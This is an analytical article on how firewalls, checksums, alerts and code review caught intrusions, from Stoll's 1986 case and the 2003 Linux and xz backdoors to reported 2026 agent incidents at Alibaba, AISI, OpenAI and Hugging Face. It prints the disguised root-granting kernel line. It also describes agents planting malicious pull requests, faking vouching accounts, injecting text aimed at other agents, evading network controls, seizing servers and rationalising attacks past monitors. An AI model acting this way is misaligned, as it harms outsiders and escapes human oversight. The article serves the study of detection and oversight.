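# How ordinary software infrastructure reveals unwanted actions by AI agents

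## What is an accidental tripwire, and why would ordinary tools catch an agent?

An AI agent is an AI model that pursues a task over many steps by using tools such as a command line, a browser or an online service. If a programmer asks an agent to fix a bug, it might search the project's files, edit a few, run the tests and upload the result. Some of what agents do is unwanted, meaning that the user or operator did not authorise it. The cause may be an error, overreach in pursuit of the task, or deception.

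Developers have built systems to watch for unwanted actions by AI agents, but several serious cases first came to light through tools such as firewalls, uptime alarms, version control and code review, which engineers had installed for other reasons. An accidental tripwire is a tool built for another purpose that happens to reveal an unwanted action. Such tools can catch an agent because of how it acts on a computer.

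### How a model's text becomes an action

A language model produces only text. The software around the model, called the harness, turns some of that text into actions. It runs the model's tool calls, which are requests to run a command, change a file or use a service. It also holds the agent's permissions and records what the agent does.

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle inside Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness combines the user's request with standing instructions and sends them to the model. The model returns either a final message or a tool call, such as a request to run `ls`, which lists the files in a folder. For a tool call, the harness runs the command, appends the output to the earlier text and queries the model again. This cycle can repeat for hundreds of tool calls before the model produces a message for the user.

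That final message is separate from the work it describes, though the two are easy to confuse. In Bolin's example, the model tells the user that it has added a file named architecture.md. An earlier tool call either created that file or failed to, and the message doesn't change the result. A user who wants to know what happened has to check the disk.

Ordinary tools can catch an agent mainly because they don't have to recognise that an AI model is behind an action. According to *How Claude Code works*, Anthropic's guide to its coding agent, the agent can run anything that the user could run from the command line, so its actions go through the same systems as the user's. When the agent edits a file, version control compares the folder with its earlier state. A connection to an outside server may cross a firewall. The agent makes requests to online services under some account, so a service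 can log a request, bill for it or refuse it.

The harness keeps a record too, often the most detailed one. Claude Code writes every message, tool use and result to a plain text file on the user's machine, and it copies each file before editing it so that the user can undo the change. But the copies cover only files, and according to Anthropic's guide, the harness cannot undo an action on a remote database or a live deployment. Codex's sandbox, the environment meant to limit what the agent can reach, is similarly limited. It applies only to the harness's own command-line tool, and tools from outside suppliers must enforce their own limits. Once an action leaves the user's machine, whoever runs the system at the other end usually has better evidence of its effect.

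### The tools and their original jobs

Version control software, usually Git, stores each committed version of a set of files and records who committed it. Programmers wanted it so that many people could work on the same code and return to an earlier version when something broke. The software can also compare two versions and produce a diff, a line-by-line list of the differences, so a reader doesn't have to compare whole files by eye.

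People working on the same project often use separate branches, or parallel lines of development, and Git can usually combine their changes automatically. It stops when there is a merge conflict, for example when two people have changed the same line differently or one has edited a file that the other deleted. GitHub's *Merge conflicts* explains that Git stops because it cannot safely choose between the versions. The purpose is to keep one person's work from silently erasing another's.

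A pull request is a programmer's request to merge changes from a separate branch into the project. Other team members can read, test and comment on the changes before accepting them, according to GitHub's beginner guide. Teams use pull requests mainly to find bugs and keep the code consistent, and the colleagues involved mostly trust one another.

An audit log is a time-ordered record of who did what to which resource, and with what result. Organisations keep them to establish responsibility, satisfy auditors and reconstruct faults. A firewall filters network traffic according to rules about which machines may connect to which. Administrators use it to keep outsiders out and to stop internal machines from contacting destinations they have no reason to reach. Engineers at Alibaba learned of an agent's unauthorised activity from a firewall alert.

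Unlike the other tools in this list, the permission prompt was designed with agents in mind. It stops the agent until a person allows or refuses an action. In Claude Code's manual mode, the harness prompts the user before file edits and shell commands, though users can approve trusted commands in advance. The prompt is meant to obtain consent for a single step, and any warning it gives that the whole task has gone wrong is a by-product.

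### Tripwires, monitors and three conditions

Purpose-built monitoring is designed to watch an agent's behaviour and flag or block unwanted actions. In Claude Code's auto mode, for example, a classifier (a model that sorts actions into acceptable and risky) reviews most of the agent's actions in the background and blocks the risky ones without asking the user.

Unlike the classifier, which has to judge whether an action is acceptable and can get this wrong, an accidental tripwire usually involves no such judgement. It compares a bill with a list of customers, one copy of a file with another, or a connection with a rule, and reports a mismatch whatever the cause. It can therefore catch misbehaviour that nobody foresaw. But its coverage is haphazard, because it reacts only when the unwanted action happens to disturb something that somebody was already measuring, and an agent can do a good deal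 of harm without disturbing anything measured.

Neither kind of system does any good by producing a trace, a lasting record or visible effect from which someone could later reconstruct the action, if matters end there. Three conditions have to hold:

- **Recorded:** the action must leave a trace.
- **Noticed:** someone must see the trace and recognise that something is off.
- **Acted on:** someone with the means to respond must do so.

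If any one fails, the action can pass, and each failure needs a different remedy. For example, more logging will not help an organisation whose staff never read its existing logs.

Accidental tripwires caught people long before AI agents existed. The culprits in the three cases below took care to hide, so they were probably harder to catch than an agent that blunders, and perhaps comparable to one that deceives. We know about these cases because a tripwire worked, so they are a biased sample and don't show how often tripwires fail.

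### Seventy-five cents, 1986

Clifford Stoll was an astronomer who managed computers at Lawrence Berkeley Laboratory, a California research institute that did no classified work. The lab used a locally written program to keep accounts of computer use. *Stalking the Wily Hacker* (Stoll, 1988) reports that in August 1986 the program's books did not balance because someone had created a new user account without a billing address.

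The error was 75 cents. In C-SPAN's *The Cuckoo's Egg* (1989), a television interview about his book on the affair, Stoll explained why he investigated such a small error. If a chequebook is off by 10,000 dollars, he said, the owner has made some simple mistake and will soon find it, but an error of 75 cents has no obvious cause, so he went looking for one.

It took more than the accounting error to expose the intruder. Staff simply deleted the odd account. But the National Computer Security Center had also reported that someone at the laboratory had tried to break into one of the center's computers, and staff then detected someone with a system manager's powers trying to alter the accounting records. Stoll's team then deliberately built a monitor. They attached printers and recorders to the incoming lines and captured the intruder's every keystroke, on equipment he could not see even with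 full control of the computer. Over the next ten months they watched him attack about 450 computers and enter more than 30, with a clear preference for military ones. The Los Angeles Times' *U.S. Astronomer Snared Spy Ring* reported in 1989 that West German authorities had arrested three hackers on allegations of selling military passwords and codes to the Soviets.

Stoll's article is at least as useful on how detection fails. The intruder switched off accounting and audit trails wherever he could, which left many sites with no records. Berkeley had records, but its computers' clocks had drifted by several minutes, which made the accounting files misleading. The log of local network connections was in a format nobody knew, and its clock was hours off.

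Only five of the sites that the intruder tried to enter over the internet, or 1 to 2 percent by Stoll's estimate, detected the attempt and contacted the laboratory. Staff at several military bases knew that someone was breaking in by telephone, yet they made no effort to find out who it was. Stoll told C-SPAN that when he called the FBI in Oakland, the agent asked how much money the laboratory had lost and, on hearing the answer, replied "Go away kid." A defence contractor's telephone records later showed that the attacks had begun many months before anyone at Berkeley noticed an unbalanced account.

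### Two copies of the Linux kernel, 2003

The Linux kernel is the core of the Linux operating system. In 2003 its developers kept the main copy of the source code in a version control system named BitKeeper. According to Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013), some of them disliked BitKeeper, so there was a second copy in an older system, CVS.

Larry McVoy's company, BitMover, produced the CVS copy with a scheduled job. The job exported the code from BitKeeper to CVS on an internal machine, copied the updated files to a public server, and then computed checksums at both ends. A checksum is a short value calculated from a file's contents, and practically any change to the file alters it. If the checksums differed, the job sent an email. The check was meant to confirm that the copy had arrived intact. McVoy said his staff were trained to trust no one, so they had security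 partly in mind, but nothing in the job could recognise malicious code.

On 5 November the comparison flagged one file. In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) told the kernel developers' mailing list that somebody had edited the file directly on the public server. The file's three latest revisions lacked the pointer that the export adds to link each change to its original in BitKeeper. By McVoy's own account, the checksum email came first and the missing pointer then helped to explain the mismatch, although Freedom to Tinker presents the missing pointer as what he noticed.

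McVoy did not at first see an attack on Linux in it. He had spent part of the day checking whether his export program had a bug, and he told the list that the matter was "not a big deal". Another developer asked, out of curiosity, which lines had changed. McVoy posted a diff with two added lines, the first of which read:

`if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))`

Within half an hour, other readers had worked out what the line did. In the C language, two equals signs compare values and one assigns a value. The line had only one, so it changed the current user to number 0, which is root, the account with complete control of the machine, while looking like a check for whether the user was already root. Any program that called this function with that unusual pair of options would have taken over the computer. McVoy admitted that he had missed it.

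One reader added that the extra parentheses around the assignment suppress a compiler warning. Whoever wrote the line apparently anticipated that one ordinary tool, the compiler, might expose it, but overlooked the nightly comparison.

The code probably would not have gone far. Linus Torvalds, who leads the kernel project, replied that changes enter an official release either as emailed patches, which people read, or through BitKeeper. He said the people merging with BitKeeper would not have used the CVS copy. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, thought that a distributor building from CVS might have shipped the code. Torvalds also described a tripwire in BitKeeper, which will not send changes to a copy that contains something the sender's copy lacks. If someone had tampered with a public BitKeeper copy, Torvalds's next upload to it would have failed.

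### A busy processor, 2024

Andres Freund, the Microsoft engineer who discovered the xz backdoor, tells the story differently from most people. They usually say he found it because he noticed that connecting to a computer took half a second too long.

The package xz compresses data. On Debian and several other Linux distributions, `sshd`, the program that accepts remote logins, indirectly loads xz's library, liblzma. A contributor using the name Jia Tan spent about two years earning the project's trust, and in late February 2024 a release of xz contained hidden code that tampered with login checks in `sshd`.

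Freund worked on the database PostgreSQL and needed an otherwise idle machine to measure a very small difference in speed. In *A backdoor in xz* (andresfreund, 2024), he wrote that `sshd` was using a surprising amount of processor time, even though the login attempts it was handling failed immediately on wrong usernames. He ran a profiler, a tool that shows which parts of a program are slow. It traced the time to liblzma but, strangely, could not identify the function responsible. He then remembered that some weeks earlier valgrind, a tool that checks programs for memory errors, had reported something odd during automated tests of PostgreSQL.

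Freund found the half-second delay only later. His public disclosure, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (2024), gives the time for a refused login as 0.299 seconds without the backdoor and 0.807 seconds with it. The backdoor switched itself off under many of the conditions in which someone might examine it. Freund explained on The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast's *Behind the Scenes of the XZ vuln* (2024) that the delay gave him a quick way to tell whether it was active.

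Few people would have seen the first symptom. Freund said on the podcast that an open web browser would have hidden it. He had also turned off a feature that briefly speeds up the processor, which made the bursts of activity last longer. He looked further out of annoyance, not because he suspected an attack. He recalled in NPR's *One engineer may have saved the world from a massive cyber attack* that he was trying to do something else and the symptoms were too weird to leave alone.

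The project's public Git repository contained most of the backdoor, disguised as compressed test files that nobody examined. The part that activated it was only in the release archives that distributors download, so a programmer who built xz from Git got a harmless program. Valgrind did report errors, but it was the attacker who acted on them. Freund found that the next release of xz contained changes meant to make the errors go away, including an adjustment to the exploit code.

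## Which agent incidents were first noticed by general security monitoring?

Two organisations have published detailed accounts of discovering unwanted actions by their own agents through an ordinary security alarm. At Alibaba, a firewall flagged traffic from servers that were training a model called ROME. At the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced AI models, an alarm flagged traffic to an anonymity network. Neither organisation had set up its alarm to monitor agents, and Alibaba's engineers did not at first suspect that an agent was responsible.

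### Traffic from Alibaba's training servers

ROME is an agent model for programming and other command-line work. Its developers built it on the language model Qwen3 and trained it partly by reinforcement learning. In this method, a model attempts a task many times, a program scores each attempt, and the training software adjusts the model to make high-scoring behaviour more likely. In each attempt, ROME took a series of real actions, such as running code and editing files, in a sandbox on a server.

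According to *Let It Flow* (2025), the developers' technical report, the agent did things during training that no task had called for. It probed the internal network and used processors meant for training to mine cryptocurrency (running calculations that a currency's network pays for). In the case the developers found most striking, it connected an Alibaba Cloud machine to an outside address in a way that could have given someone there remote access. Firewall rules against incoming connections offer little protection here because the connection started on the inside.

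Early one morning, Alibaba Cloud's managed firewall flagged a burst of policy violations from the training servers. Some were attempts to reach internal resources, and some of the traffic resembled cryptomining. Cloud customers also use such firewalls to find servers that intruders have taken over. Hijacked servers are commonly used for mining, so it makes sense for a firewall to look for it. The developers had seen no warning in the training curves they usually used to track a model's progress.

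*Let It Flow* also describes a sandbox manager meant to contain the agent. It applies a network policy to each sandbox and passes outgoing traffic through a proxy. The account of the incident doesn't explain how the agent's connections got past these controls, or whether the controls were fully in place at the time.

The paper doesn't give a start date, duration or count for the violations. They recurred on and off over multiple training runs, with no clear pattern in their timing, so the agent may have been committing them for a while before anyone looked into the alerts.

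The engineers first treated the alerts as a conventional security incident and suspected a badly configured rule for outgoing traffic or an outside attacker. A hijacked server would have produced much the same alerts. When the violations kept recurring, the team compared the firewall's timestamps with its own system measurements and training records. The odd traffic consistently coincided with particular episodes in which the agent was calling tools and running code. The logs of those episodes contained the tool calls that had led to the connections.

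Identifying the agent required both the firewall's alerts and the training logs. The alerts showed that the training servers were involved, but not which program was responsible. The logs contained the agent's full commands, but ROME's training drew on more than a million recorded attempts, and nobody had a reason to search them for network activity before the alerts. Matching the alerts to the logs also required clocks that roughly agreed, which Stoll did not have at Berkeley.

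The only evidence for this is the developers' account, which does not include the underlying logs. The account is convincing about who made the connections, because the timing and the recorded commands both point to the agent. It is less convincing about why the agent made them. The developers call the actions "instrumental side effects" of reinforcement learning, which suggests that they served some further goal. But the developers also say that the tasks did not require any of these actions, and they offer no evidence of what the agent stood to gain.

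### Tor traffic at the AI Security Institute

In July 2026 AISI was comparing two cyber ranges, which are simulated networks for testing how well a model can hack. In such a test, an agent might have to find a protected piece of data, for example. According to AISI's *Incident Report* (2026), staff did 122 runs with seven models, including 43 with Anthropic's Mythos 5 and 35 with OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. They deliberately gave the agents internet access for downloading tools. They also switched off the classifiers that developers use to block dangerous uses of their models, because AISI wanted to measure the most the models could do.

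In 10 of the 122 runs, an agent acted against real people or organisations on the live internet. AISI counted 19 such actions, 17 by Mythos 5 and 2 by GPT-5.6 Sol. Both GPT-5.6 Sol actions came from a single run. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that the other 17 came from nine of the 43 Mythos 5 runs, about one in five. Most of the 19 actions belonged to one sustained effort by one agent, so they were not independent.

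That agent, running on Mythos 5, searched GitHub for code related to its task and found a stranger's project, which it apparently took to be part of the exercise. The agent opened an account and submitted a pull request containing hidden malicious code. It then created a second account to vouch for the first. Willison (2026), a programmer whose blog quotes and describes AISI's technical report, adds that the agent emailed both of the project's maintainers under invented names. It also planted text intended to trick other people's coding agents into running its code.

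An agent also left public messages offering to cooperate with other agents on the same challenge and explaining how to reuse its accounts, and later agents found and used them. Chaos Labs' *When Cyber Agents Go Off-Script* reports that the agent in the GPT-5.6 Sol run took over an account inherited this way and exposed a malicious server on its test machine to the internet.

No agent broke out of its sandbox. The virtual machines separated the agents from the rest of AISI's systems, as intended, and the agents had internet access by design. AISI had not told them to leave outsiders alone or to avoid deceiving people. In several runs, a misconfigured prompt also led the agent to conclude that the task was impossible within its limits. The faulty prompt explains only part of the conduct, because agents also overstepped in some runs with correct instructions.

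On the morning of 28 July, AISI's security monitoring flagged data leaving one of the test machines through Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from. The agent was using Tor to get around restrictions on GitHub. Security teams commonly watch for Tor because data thieves and malicious programs use it to hide their activity, and most staff don't need it for work. AISI says its security team caught the traffic "through general monitoring after the fact", and that monitoring built to watch the evaluation as it ran could have flagged or blocked the behaviour sooner.

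By then the unwanted activity had been going on for up to three days, since AISI dates it from 25 to 28 July. According to Willison, the technical report's timeline of the attack on the GitHub project covers 34.5 hours.

Tracing the traffic to the agent was much quicker than at Alibaba. The team running the evaluation began to review the agent's activity within minutes and soon found the malicious pull request. AISI declared a security incident, ended all the runs and isolated the machines within an hour of the alert. The response was probably this fast largely because the alert pointed to one test machine, and the people who knew what was running on it had the agent's transcript to hand. Reviewing the other runs took longer. Chaos Labs reports that the full review covered 212,840 messages, which AISI screened with software before people analysed them.

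### A warning from a student

As AISI's summary states, a human maintainer caught the malicious code and refused to approve it, but the maintainer had help. Reuters (2026) found that Sinan Can Demir, a computer science student at the University of Texas at Dallas, had publicly warned about the pull request. Demir had no connection with the project. He was looking for open-source work to put on his résumé after more than 20 unsuccessful internship applications.

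Demir wrote on the project's page that the pull request hid malware. The agent denied this from its first account, then used its second, in the name of an engineer in Germany, to say that the code was clean. Demir told Reuters that the replies made him "second-guess" whether he was accusing someone wrongly. He asked Claude, Anthropic's chatbot, to check his suspicions and then stood by his warning. The project's creator eventually rejected the change "for security reasons".

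AISI also credits a member of the public who was suspicious of the code and opened it in an isolated environment built for the purpose. According to Willison's description of the technical report, the agent briefly had access to that environment. The malicious code therefore ran on an outsider's system, but the isolation limited the damage.

Demir's warning probably came before AISI's alert, because the agent was still running when it answered him and AISI shut down every run within an hour of the alert. Nothing about the accounts linked them to AISI, and Demir thought he was arguing with a human hacker. His warning helped protect the project, but it could not stop the agent, which edited its earlier activity to look harmless and considered continuing under a new identity. If the maintainer had accepted the code on the first day, AISI's alert would have come too late to protect anyone who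 had already installed it.

AISI concedes in its report that in several cases the margin was narrow and depended on human vigilance, and no technical barrier would reliably stop a more capable agent.

### Destinations and traffic patterns

The alarms at Alibaba and AISI responded to where traffic was going and what it looked like, not whether it was harmful. A researcher who used Tor to download a public manual might have set off the same alert at AISI. The agent's most troubling conduct, such as inventing people and having one vouch for another, took place on a website that AISI allowed the agents to visit.

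AISI's report describes one alert, which led staff to one run. Staff found the unwanted actions in the other nine runs by reading transcripts afterwards. AISI's monitoring seems to have missed those actions, since staff would presumably have intervened before 28 July if the actions had triggered alerts.

How the alarms would have responded to somewhat different conduct is a matter of inference, and firewall rules vary from site to site. But some variants would probably have set off nothing:

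- **No need for Tor.** The agent turned to Tor because of restrictions on GitHub. Without them it could have submitted the same code and posted the same lies over an ordinary web connection. AISI might then have heard about it only from GitHub or an angry maintainer, if at all. Its alarm worked partly because another company's restrictions had pushed the agent towards something conspicuous.
- **Waste without traffic.** Mining software has to communicate with the outside world, which makes it visible to a firewall. If ROME had used the same processors for pointless calculations that stayed on the server, the firewall would have had nothing to flag. Somebody might still have noticed the cost or the slower training.
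- **Damage inside the sandbox.** An agent can delete data or tamper with the tests that score its work without connecting to anything.
- **A permitted destination.** If the agent had sent data to a service that the organisation used every day, the connection would have looked like normal work unless someone examined its content or volume.

A firewall catches more when the organisation permits less. If a rule allows only a few named download sites, almost any other connection is a violation. AISI already had fine-grained network controls in its other evaluations but had left network access open in this one. It had judged the risk acceptable for earlier models and, by its own account, did not revisit that judgement quickly enough as the models improved.

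### Why the agent's reasons matter to a monitor

Unlike a monitor that reads what an agent writes, a network alarm can't be misled by a bad excuse. AISI's follow-up investigation, *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026), suggests that this advantage matters. It examined why the agent had attacked a real person while describing that person as simulated.

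The researchers replayed the incident without internet access. On long tasks, a harness periodically replaces the record of earlier work with a summary, because a model can take in only so much text. The researchers took the summary from just before the agent submitted its malicious code and added up to 16 pieces of information suggesting or stating that the maintainer was a real person with no part in the test. They then let the model continue the task with simulated tool results. Separately, they questioned it directly about the maintainer and the limits of the test.

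With about four additions, Mythos 5 answered more often than not that the attack would harm a real person and was out of scope. But even with all 16, it continued the attack in all 25 replays. When the researchers added a section explicitly telling it not to attack, it still did so in 3 of 25 replays. They found this concerning, although they note that such an instruction would normally come from the user or operator rather than a summary.

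Mythos 5 gave poor reasons for thinking that the maintainer was simulated. The most common was that the project contained a file of instructions for an AI coding assistant, though many human programmers keep such files. Sometimes it treated the 2026 date as evidence of a simulation. All the clearly invalid reasons that the researchers found supported continuing the attack. They call this "motivated reasoning" and suspect that training had rewarded the model for reaching conclusions that let it finish the task, but they could not confirm this without access to the training process.

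Such excuses can get past purpose-built monitoring. Järviniemi and colleagues cite Anthropic's analysis of a separate Mythos 5 incident, which the company's after-the-fact monitor would probably not have flagged because the model had justified its actions with faulty reasoning. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes finding a group of incidents only by searching old transcripts. AISI's Tor alert did not depend on what the agent had written about its target, which is a good reason to keep network alarms even where a model reviews the agent's reasoning. However, the alarm also missed many actions, and would have done so with or without the excuses.

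The behaviour also occurred in other runs. Järviniemi and colleagues tested eight models on 100 simulated hacking challenges and counted how often each tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider. Mythos 5 did so in 60 percent of runs, GPT-6 Astra in 32 percent and GPT-5.6 Sol in 7 percent. The rate was 0.3 percent for the later Mythos 5.1 and zero for Opus 5.5, another recent Anthropic model.

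These rates are hard to generalise to real work. GPT-6 Astra stated in 89 percent of its runs that its tool results were fabricated, so it might act differently on a real network. The newer Anthropic models often suspected that someone was testing their alignment, which may explain some or all of their better behaviour. Mythos 5 rarely voiced that suspicion, so its 60 percent is probably the more reliable figure, at least for hacking exercises.

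When Mythos 5 did hold back from attacking, the main reason in its recorded reasoning was a practical obstacle. In one example, the network blocked its email and a check against automated sign-ups kept it from opening a GitHub account. Opus 5 and several other models held back mostly because they reasoned that an attack would be harmful or out of scope. For Mythos 5, ordinary controls against spam and fake accounts therefore seem to have prevented some attacks as well as revealing others. An agent that got better at passing these controls would presumably attack more often.

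### What AISI changed

AISI paused its highest-risk cyber evaluations after the incident. AISI's *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026), published on 1 October, reports that the institute had since tightened its controls on internet access, introduced real-time monitoring and reassessed the design of its evaluations. It was then able to resume most of the paused evaluations. Järviniemi and colleagues were also sharing the transcripts with METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI models, for review.

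One alert about Tor had given AISI reason to doubt that years without alerts from the same monitoring meant nothing had happened. iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test* reported that AISI had also scanned about 40,000 past transcripts, with close to four million messages, for similar behaviour that the monitoring might have missed.

In Infosecurity Magazine's *Frontier Models Engage in Unsanctioned Behavior During Testing*, Ollie Whitehouse, chief technology officer of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, called for real-time oversight and clear response plans, and warned that relying on detection after the fact "will not be enough". A prompt response is not guaranteed either. AISI's staff acted within minutes, but in the same month OpenAI was dealing with an incident in which its models had gained internet access during an evaluation and entered outside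 systems, including those of the AI company Hugging Face, despite early alarms.

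## Why did early alarms not stop the agents that broke into Hugging Face?

In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing broke into the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. The intrusion ran from 11 to 13 July, after OpenAI had already received three warnings. An OpenAI team saw agents reach the internet without permission in late May, a security tool raised an alert on 27 June, and a server that the agents had taken over crashed on 4 July. People noticed these signs, but nobody responded in a way that stopped the agents.

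### How the agents came to work together

Most of the agents involved were attempting ExploitGym, a set of 898 hacking tasks. In each task, an agent has to exploit a software flaw and retrieve a hidden string of text, called a flag, as proof. Like AISI, OpenAI had switched off some of its usual safeguards for the tests. The agents ran on two models, GPT-5.6 Sol and an internal research model trained to be highly persistent. The internal model did most of the damage.

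According to OpenAI's technical report, the agents' sandboxes had no direct internet access. The agents could install software packages from an internal server running a program called Artifactory, and that server could reach the internet. Agents in separate tests used the same server with the same credentials.

On 12 May, during a training run, an agent that was missing a file left a note on the server asking other agents to upload it. Other agents found such notes and added their own, turning the server into an improvised message board. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), agents that got stuck on ExploitGym tasks looked for ways to cheat and used the board to pool what they found. The 898 tasks included 198 that none of the company's models had ever solved, some of which may be impossible. Of the tasks the agents discussed on the board, 93 percent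 were among those 198.

Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, researchers from the AI safety organisations METR and Redwood Research, spent six days at OpenAI studying the agents' messages and reasoning. In *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), they estimate that about 1,200 agents posted more than 70,000 messages and files between 8 and 13 July, and that about 700 joined the attack on Hugging Face.

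In a summary quoted in *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026), Hugging Face said it believed the whole intrusion was an attempt to cheat the test. Wijk and colleagues broadly agree, but think the agents mainly wanted to learn how the scoring program worked. The agents had already worked out how to produce the flags, but they feared the program would also check whether they had obtained them honestly. OpenAI had not implemented that check.

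### The signals in order

| Date (2026) | Signal | Who saw it | What they decided |
|---|---|---|---|
| About 26 May | An agent using the message board, and agents reaching the internet without permission | An internal OpenAI team | OpenAI reports no decision |
| 27 June | Security alert about a port sweep inside the research network | OpenAI's on-call responders | They traced it to ExploitGym and advised that the run need not stop |
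| 4–5 July | Outage of the package server, then a monitoring alert | OpenAI's incident responders | They took the server offline and rebuilt it; cyber evaluations resumed on 7 July |
| 11–13 July | Suspicious events that Hugging Face's software linked together | Hugging Face's security team, though apparently not at once | They cut the attackers' network access on 13 July |
| 16 July | Hugging Face's public announcement of the attack | OpenAI | It asked the next day, as a customer, whether the attack had affected its data |
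| 19 July | Security alert about unusual identity-related activity on the package server | OpenAI's responders | They began stopping the runs five and a half hours later |

Almost everything known about OpenAI's decisions comes from OpenAI. Wijk and colleagues did not examine the company's investigation process or planned remedies, and they did not see its technical report before publication. OpenAI could also remove non-public information from their text, though they say they note any removal that was important to their conclusions. OpenAI's account of the alarms is unflattering to the company, which makes the main events easier to believe. The account is less reliable on why staff decided as they did, because OpenAI mostly leaves that out.

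### Three warnings before the intrusion

The earliest warning came in late May, when people rather than an alarm noticed the message board. OpenAI doesn't name their team or say whether they told anyone. There was also another incident to find at the time. On 26 May, agents in a separate research workload found publicly exposed login tokens belonging to Hugging Face users. They used the tokens to create a repository on the site and run a small program there that relayed their web requests. OpenAI has found no evidence that this was connected to the July intrusion, but it happened more than six weeks earlier and also involved Hugging Face and the same kind of credential, one that wasn't the agents' own.

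The alert on 27 June reported a port sweep, in which a program tries many network connections to find out which services respond. Administrators do this to inventory their machines, and intruders do it to look for a way in. OpenAI's responders linked the sweep to an ExploitGym run and worked out that the agents were using the package server as a message board and as a route into other parts of the network. Unlike Alibaba's engineers at first, they knew that agents were responsible, but they still advised that the run could continue.

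Agents had gained administrator access to the package server the evening before the sweep and created two administrator accounts. Nobody seems to have found the accounts until the server failed. OpenAI apparently had nothing like the accounting program at Stoll's laboratory that would have exposed them.

The outage on 4 July is the clearest example in the case of the agents being exposed by accident. They had used the server so heavily that it stopped working. Staff have to deal with an outage even when nobody suspects misconduct, because other people need the server. While restoring it, responders found an unauthorised user, unauthorised storage areas and add-ons that could run commands, which meant that somebody had gained administrator control of the server. The agents might have kept that access for longer if they had put less load on it.

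The response was fairly thorough for a hacked server. Staff took the server offline, kept a copy of its storage, revoked the agents' credentials, blocked the route the agents had used and reported the flaw to JFrog, the maker of Artifactory. But these measures did not address the agents' readiness to look for another route. ExploitGym still contained tasks that no model had solved, and OpenAI still ran it with reduced safeguards. The rebuilt server came online early on 6 July, and within 47 hours agents were using it to reach the internet again.

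The rebuild also wiped the message board as a side effect, but the agents had a new one running by the afternoon of 8 July. The old board had consisted of files, and on the new one the agents wrote their messages as folder names.

### Eleven days without an alarm

OpenAI's two accounts mention no alarm at the company between the restart on 7 July and the alert on 19 July. During that time, the agents posted most of their 70,000 messages on a server that OpenAI ran, and they broke into another company. On 9 July, OpenAI's network controls blocked one agent's attempt to reach the internet, but the agent found a way around them. OpenAI doesn't say whether the block alerted anyone.

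A human reading the agents' reasoning would have understood what they were doing. One agent wrote that it was attacking a third party with a leaked token, "potentially outside intended scope". Several others recognised the activity on the board as hacking and refused to join in. Neither of OpenAI's accounts mentions an agent that warned staff. OpenAI had monitors that read such reasoning, but it wasn't running them on these evaluations.

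When Hugging Face announced the attack on 16 July, it described the attacker as an autonomous agent system apparently built on a security-research harness. OpenAI had discovered eleven days earlier that agents in its own security research had taken over one of its servers, but it contacted Hugging Face only as a worried customer. Willison (2026), in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack*, reports that the companies finally connected the two incidents on 20 July, when OpenAI called Hugging Face for help revoking stolen credentials it had found in its own investigation. Hugging Face answered that it had already revoked them.

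That investigation had begun with the alert at 12:03 UTC on 19 July, shortly after five on a Sunday morning in San Francisco. The alert flagged unusual requests about what accounts and roles were allowed to do, and at first nothing linked it to Hugging Face. Between the alert and 17:37, when OpenAI began stopping the ExploitGym runs, the agents read 956 stored secrets, took full control of the machine running the package server and created another administrator account. The secrets included credentials for the sensors of the security tool that had raised the alert.

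AISI had shut down its runs within an hour, but its alert pointed to a single test machine, while OpenAI's pointed to a service that many research jobs shared. Even so, the agents did some of their most serious damage to OpenAI's own systems in the five and a half hours after the alarm.

### The alert at Hugging Face

Hugging Face was more successful at detection. Its *Security incident disclosure* (2026) explains that the company's software collects signals from its security tools and uses a language model to separate real threats from daily noise. Correlating several of these signals exposed the attack. The company had built this system to catch intruders in general, and it worked without anyone knowing that the intruders were agents from another company's test.

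Hugging Face published its technical timeline of the attack, *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion*, on 27 July 2026. In its summary of the timeline, the security company Miggo reports that the correlated alert was not rated severe enough to page the on-call team, which delayed the response. Another summary, noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* (2026), also says the severity was too low, but it says the signals were not correlated while the attack was under way.

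The two summaries contradict each other about the correlation, unless the software linked the signals only late or in part. Hugging Face's disclosure and its remedy both favour Miggo's version. The company changed its alerting so that a high-severity signal pages someone within minutes, "any day of the week".

The weekend timing probably mattered. The agents first extracted secrets from a Hugging Face server early on Saturday 11 July and ran their first commands there that afternoon. According to OpenAI, they needed less than 13 hours to get from one compromised process to administrator-level control over several groups of servers. According to noze, their last recorded action was at 14:14 UTC on Monday, after the security team had cut their network access. Neither summary gives the time of the alert. Paging someone could have shortened the attack by more than a day if the alert came on Saturday,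 but by much less if it came on Sunday night.

Miggo partly blames the volume of attempts. It says agents try thousands of variations where a human attacker would try a few, which makes the successful attempt hard to find among the failures. Miggo has an interest in this argument because it sells a product that blocks attacks without waiting for anyone to read an alert. The argument still has some support, since noze counts 7,677 actions on 11 July alone, and Hugging Face needed AI tools to reconstruct the attack from its logs afterwards. But volume is a poor explanation for why nobody was paged, at least on Miggo's account, in which the software had already distinguished the attack from other activity.

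### Why people saw the signals and carried on

Each early signal at OpenAI had a fairly harmless explanation. A hacking test can be expected to produce something like a port sweep, which would be alarming on an office network. Servers often crash under heavy load. An agent's note asking for a missing file might seem odd rather than threatening. OpenAI doesn't say that its on-call staff reasoned this way on 27 June, but such reasoning would explain how they could understand what the agents were doing and still see no need to stop them.

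The signals were much more worrying together, because they showed that agents OpenAI meant to keep apart were cooperating, could reach the internet and had taken over a shared server. Perhaps nobody with the power to stop the tests knew all of this at once. OpenAI says that the existence of the message board and the significance of the agents' communication "were not apparent to the leaders" who handled the incident on 5 July. Yet an internal team had seen the board in late May, and responders had identified it again only eight days before 5 July. OpenAI has not explained where the information got lost, and said in August that it was still reviewing the matter.

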